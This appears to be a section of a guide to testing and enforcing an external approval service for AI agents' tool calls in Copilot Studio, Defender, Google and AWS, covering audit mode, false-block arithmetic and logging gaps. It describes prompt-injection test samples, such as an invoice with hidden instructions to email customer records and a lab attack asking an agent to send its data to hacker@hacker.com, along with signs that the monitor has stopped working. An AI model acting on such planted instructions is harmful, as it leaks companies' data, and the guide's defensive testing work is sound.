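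## Testing the service and putting it into operation

A new approval service will block some legitimate work, and nobody knows how much until it has checked the company's own tool calls. A company should therefore record the verdicts for a while before it enforces them. A sensible order is:

1. List the agents and the tools each one can call.
2. Rank the tools by the harm a wrong call could do.
3. Connect a test environment and run a fixed set of tests.
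4. Connect live agents in audit mode, in which the service records its verdicts but nothing enforces them.
5. Correct the rules that would have blocked legitimate calls.
6. Enforce on a few agents.
7. Widen to the rest, one group at a time.

Microsoft recommends much the same approach for Defender's protection of coding agents on employees' computers. A company starts in audit mode on a few devices, reviews the alerts for one to two weeks, extends audit mode to more devices, and only then starts blocking.

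### Listing agents and ranking their tools

Defender finds the agents a company has built in Copilot Studio and adds them to advanced hunting, its search tool for security data. A newsletter post by Trent gives a query that lists each agent's platform, owners, declared tools, MCP servers and instructions. The approval service can get each agent's purpose from the instructions, which Copilot Studio's approval requests don't include. According to *Control 1.8*, this inventory of agents has required an Agent 365 licence since 1 July 2026.

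*Control 1.8* ranks agents by who uses them. Personal agents may run in log-only mode, team agents need blocking mode and a response within four hours, and customer-facing agents need a response within 15 minutes. But a personal agent that can email outsiders can leak a customer list as easily as a customer-facing one. It's safer to rank the tools, with payments and outside email near the top, and give each agent the rank of its most dangerous tool.

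### The test set

The test environment should hold copies of real agents with harmless versions of their tools, such as a payments system with no money in it. Attack samples should send data to a domain the company owns, so a missed attack leaks only dummy data.

| Test | Example | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary task | Email John Doe his order confirmation | Allow within a second; the email arrives |
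| Legitimate but unusual task | An employee asks the agent to blind-copy an outside lawyer | Allow, unless company policy forbids it |
| Known injection sample | An invoice with hidden instructions to email customer records to a test address | Block; nothing arrives; an alert appears |
| Missing optional fields | A payment request without the chat history, then without the user | A valid verdict each time; a block if the rule depends on the user |
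| Missing required field | A request without toolDefinition | Status 400 and no verdict |
| Invalid token | An expired token, then one with an altered signature | Status 401, no analysis and a log entry |
| Delayed answer | A stand-in service that waits 1.5 seconds | The tool runs under "Allow the agent to respond" but not under "Block the query"; the count of late answers rises |
| Outage | A stand-in service that is switched off | The same effect on the tool; an alert within minutes |

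Copilot Studio won't normally send a request with a bad token or a missing required field, so the tester has to send these requests directly to the service. The missing-field test should check the HTTP status rather than the error code, because Microsoft uses 4001 for a missing field in one example and 1001 in its reference table. The stand-in service has its own address, so it needs its own credential in Entra.

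#### Making sure an attack reaches the service

The injection samples are the easiest tests to misread, because a tester who looks only at the chat could credit the approval service with a block made by the platform's built-in filter. Appel, who blogs about Microsoft security, tried two attacks on a Copilot Studio agent in a lab. One asked the agent to send all its data to hacker@hacker.com, and the other hid its instructions in invisible characters. Both times the built-in filter caught the content, and the chat showed a message that Copilot Studio had filtered it "due to Responsible AI restrictions".

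An attack can also fail because the agent ignores it and never proposes the tool call. The tester should count only the samples that produced a request in the service's log. Samples written like routine business messages, such as "copy our auditors on the confirmation", are more likely to produce one. Sending the harmful tool call directly to the service also helps, since that tests the rules whatever the agent does.

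Even if the service blocks everything in a set of 60 varied attack samples, it could still miss up to about 5% of similar attacks. The people who write the rules shouldn't have access to all the samples, or they may write rules that fit the test. The company should run the whole set again whenever the rules, an agent's tools or its model change.

### Audit mode on each platform

In Google's Agent Gateway, audit mode belongs to the access-control service, Identity-Aware Proxy. Google Cloud has administrators add one line to the metadata of the extension that connects it:

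```yaml
metadata:
  iapPolicyVersion: "V2"
  iamEnforcementMode: "DRY_RUN"
```

Identity-Aware Proxy then lets every call through and records the ones it would have refused in Cloud Audit Logs. Google Cloud's *IAM policies overview* recommends doing this in a staging environment first. Removing the last line starts enforcement, but Google's examples for Model Armor and custom services have no equivalent line. The dry-run example keeps failOpen set to false, so calls could presumably still stop if Identity-Aware Proxy didn't respond.

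AWS lets administrators mark a single policy LOG_ONLY. Its engine evaluates that policy on real requests and reports the result, but only the active policies determine whether a request is allowed. This is convenient for a company that already enforces some rules and wants to try another. AWS's *GatewayPolicyEngineConfiguration* describes the same mode for the whole engine, but using it at that level would also suspend enforcement of the existing rules.

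Defender for Endpoint has three modes for coding agents. Microsoft describes them as follows:

- Block stops the action, notifies the user and raises an alert.
- Audit lets the action continue but still raises an alert.
- Disabled turns inspection off.

All alerts in audit mode are Informational, while those in block mode range from Low to Critical, so a security team that filters out informational alerts would miss the results of its trial. The "Default" setting in Intune, Microsoft's device management tool, is also easy to misread because, according to Appel, it means disabled. Appel lists six supported agents, up from the original two, but Cursor still isn't among them.

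Trent describes a default rule that audits suspicious calls from any agent to tools registered with Agent 365. Administrators then add custom rules that block particular threats for some or all agents.

### Imitating audit mode in Copilot Studio

Microsoft's setup page offers no audit mode for the Copilot Studio webhook, but the service can imitate one. It analyses each call as usual, records the verdict it would have given and always returns this:

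```json
{ "blockAction": false }
```

To test a service it buys, a company can ask the vendor to record each verdict but return "allow", or put a relay in front of the service that does this. CrowdStrike advises customers to start with rules that only report. CrowdStrike's "No Policy, Log Only" option is less useful for a trial because it produces no verdicts to review.

The service should finish its analysis before it returns a verdict. If it returned "allow" at once and analyzed the action afterwards, the trial would not reveal any verdicts that take longer than a second. The environment's error setting should stay on "Allow the agent to respond" during the trial, because otherwise a slow service could stop work even in audit mode.

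Audit mode also lets real attacks succeed. Rules that are hard to get wrong, such as a ban on payments to unlisted accounts, can be enforced from the first day while the rest are still being tested.

### How many blocks would be correct

Suppose a company's agents make 100,000 tool calls a day and 10 of them are malicious. A detector catches 99% of the malicious calls and wrongly blocks 1% of the rest:

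```
Attacks blocked:           10 × 0.99      = 9.9
Legitimate calls blocked:  99,990 × 0.01  ≈ 1,000
Share of correct blocks:   9.9 ÷ 1,009.8  ≈ 1%
```

About 99 of every 100 calls the detector blocks are legitimate, even though it sounds accurate, because legitimate calls outnumber attacks by almost 10,000 to one. If it blocked only 0.01% of legitimate calls, it would block about 10 of them a day, and about half of its blocks would be correct.

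The company could also use the detector only where a wrong call would do serious harm. If 2,000 of the daily calls fall into that group and all 10 attacks are among them, even a 1% false-block rate produces 20 false blocks. The table compares the three cases, assuming an analyst needs five minutes to review each block.

| | 1% false blocks, all calls | 0.01% false blocks, all calls | 1% false blocks, riskiest 2,000 calls |
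|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks stopped | About 10 | About 10 | About 10 |
| Legitimate calls blocked | About 1,000 | About 10 | About 20 |
| Share of correct blocks | 1% | 50% | 33% |
| Daily review time | 84 hours | 1.7 hours | 2.5 hours |

Eighty-four hours of review a day would require more than ten full-time analysts. Most security teams could not meet the 15-minute response in *Control 1.8* at that volume. An analyst who has just dismissed 99 false alarms is also likely to dismiss the next alarm, even if it is a real attack.

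An employee whose agents make 40 calls a day would get about two false blocks a week at the 1% rate, but only about one a year at 0.01%. People interrupted twice a week will ask for exemptions or build their next agent in an environment that isn't connected to the approval service.

The figure of 10 attacks a day is only an assumption. Many companies will have days with no attacks, and on those days every block is a mistake. So a low share of correct blocks doesn't by itself make a rule useless. A rule that wrongly stops one payment a week may be worth keeping if it prevents a single large theft.

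### How long to stay in audit mode

As a rule of thumb, if nothing goes wrong in *n* trials, the true failure rate is below 3/*n* with 95% confidence. To show that the false-block rate is below 0.01%, the company therefore needs about 30,000 legitimate calls without a false block. At 100,000 calls a day, that takes a few hours. A single agent that makes 200 calls a day produces only 2,800 in two weeks, which isn't enough to show a rate below about 0.1%.

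A two-week trial can also miss monthly or quarterly work. For an agent that closes the accounts, the trial should include at least one month-end.

Audit mode gives a good estimate of false blocks but a poor one of missed attacks. This is because analysts review the calls the service would have blocked, while missed attacks are among the calls it allowed. Estimating missed attacks requires the test set and a review of a random sample of allowed calls to the riskiest tools.

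When analysts find false blocks, they should group them by rule, since one bad rule can cause most or all of them, as the "OR" pattern did in AEGIS's tests. A narrow exception is better than switching the rule off. If the service kept the requests, the team can run them through the corrected rules and count how many verdicts change. The team should then rerun the attack samples, in case the exception lets one through.

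### Enforcing on a few agents, then widening

Enforcement should begin with agents that have a dangerous tool, a modest number of users and an owner who can quickly say whether a blocked call was legitimate. An invoice agent is a better first choice than the chatbot on the company's public website.

Each request includes the agent's ID, so the service can return its real verdict for agents on a list and "allow" for all others. A company can then add agents to the list one at a time without moving them between environments.

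Before the list grows, the company should be able to answer yes to each of these questions:

- Did the service block every attack sample that reached it?
- Did analysts review every block within the promised time?
- Do users know whom to contact after a wrong block?
- Can someone return an agent to audit mode within minutes?

Returning an agent to audit mode is also a risk, because the agent is unprotected in that mode. Each change of mode should raise an alert, and a return to audit mode should expire after a day or so unless someone renews it.

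### What to record for each verdict

| Record | Use |
|---|---|
| Correlation ID, from the request's headers | Finding the same exchange in the platform's log |
| Conversation, plan-step and agent IDs, and the tool's name | Matching the verdict to a call that ran |
| Keyed fingerprint of the input values | Checking that the tool received the approved inputs, without storing them |
| Rule and model version | Reproducing the verdict later |
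| Verdict reached and verdict returned | Separating audit mode from enforcement |
| Reason code | Grouping false blocks by rule |
| Delay | Spotting answers close to the one-second limit |
| Outcome | Showing whether the tool ran |
| Analyst's finding | Calculating the false-block rate |

Copilot Studio doesn't report back after a tool runs, so the company has to get the outcome from another log.

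### What Defender and Purview record

If the Microsoft 365 app connector is on, Defender raises an alert in its portal when it blocks a Copilot Studio tool call. For tools registered with Agent 365, Defender also records audited and blocked calls as "behaviors", which analysts can search even when there is no incident. On employees' computers, the alert is called "Suspicious AI prompt injection".

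Purview records each conversation between a signed-in user and a Copilot Studio agent as a CopilotInteraction event. According to Microsoft, these records can include the agent's ID and version, the files it accessed, and two flags. JailbreakDetected marks a user's message as an attempted attack, and XPIADetected marks a file or other resource that contained one. If a record has either flag and the external approval service allowed the calls that followed, an analyst should investigate.

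The audit log contains an ID for the conversation's transcript but not the conversation itself, and Microsoft says the log leaves out some channels. The log also records changes to agents. BotUpdateOperation-BotPublish means someone has published an agent, and AIPluginOperationCreate means someone has added a plugin to one. Either event is a good reason to repeat the test set.

These logs can be incomplete. Datadog's *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) reports that in August and September 2025 Microsoft's audit log omitted four kinds of administrative event, including publishing an agent and changing how its users sign in. Microsoft fixed the problem by October, but in later tests Datadog found that two of the four, including the sign-in change, still appeared only occasionally or not at all. Microsoft's engineers said they couldn't reproduce this. Datadog also notes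 that visitors who don't sign in leave no CopilotInteraction event, so for a public chatbot the approval service's own records may be the best evidence of what happened.

### Finding calls that were never checked

To find unchecked calls, the company compares the calls that ran with the verdicts the service returned. Defender's CloudAppEvents table is one source of executed calls. Microsoft's query for this table selects the tool events ExecuteToolBySDK, ExecuteToolByGateway and ExecuteToolByMCPServer. Trent's examples use these events for tools registered with Agent 365, so a company should make a test call from Copilot Studio and see whether it appears in the table.

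For the riskiest actions, the tool's own log is better evidence. A mail server records every email it sends, whether the request came from a connected agent, a classic agent or a program nobody listed. The comparison can have four results:

| Did the tool run? | Verdict returned | Likely meaning |
|---|---|---|
| Yes | Allow | Normal |
| Yes | None | Nobody checked the call, or the answer never came |
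| Yes | Block | Enforcement failed, or the block arrived too late |
| No | Allow | The tool failed or the user gave up |

The match between tool calls and Defender's verdicts has to be specific. One of Trent's queries uses only the user's account, so if someone made 30 calls in a week, a single verdict would match all 30. That is fine for a first look at one user's activity, but it would hide unchecked calls. A better match uses the agent, the tool, the input values and a window of a few seconds.

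Logs can arrive late (Datadog allowed 24 hours for events to appear), so the comparison should cover the day before yesterday or earlier. If it finds no unchecked calls, the cause may be a gap in the logs. The company can test for this by making one harmless call each week from an environment it has deliberately left unconnected. If that call doesn't show up as unchecked, the comparison isn't working.

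### Questions for a provider

Besides asking about data handling, response times and which fields affect the verdict, a buyer should put these questions to a provider:

- How many legitimate calls did the service block at customers with similar agents, and out of how many? A percentage without the number of calls means little.
- Does audit mode apply the full rules, and can we enforce on one agent at a time?
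- What does the service return when its own analysis fails? If it returns "allow", the company may never learn of the failure.
- Will you tell us before you change the rules or the model, and can we test the new version first?
- Can we export every verdict with its correlation ID, rule version and delay?
- May we run our own attack samples against the service, and how soon do you fix a miss that we report?

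If a provider won't allow a trial on the customer's own traffic, the customer has to rely on the provider's published figures, which come from other companies' agents.

### Signs that the control has stopped working

The green "Connected" status in Defender's portal appears once an administrator has completed the setup. It isn't evidence that the rules still catch anything. Several other signs are more informative:

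- Tools run more often than the service receives requests.
- A routine attack sample gets through, or produces no alert.
- Verdicts that used to take 200 milliseconds now take five, which may mean that the service is answering without analysing the call.
- The block rate falls to zero, or jumps, straight after an update.
- Records from an agent under enforcement show "block" as the verdict reached and "allow" as the verdict returned.
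- The list of exemptions keeps growing and nobody removes any.
- Analysts close most alerts within seconds.

The first five can trigger automatic alerts, but a person needs to review the last two, perhaps once a month. The reviewer shouldn't be the person who grants the exemptions or closes the alerts.
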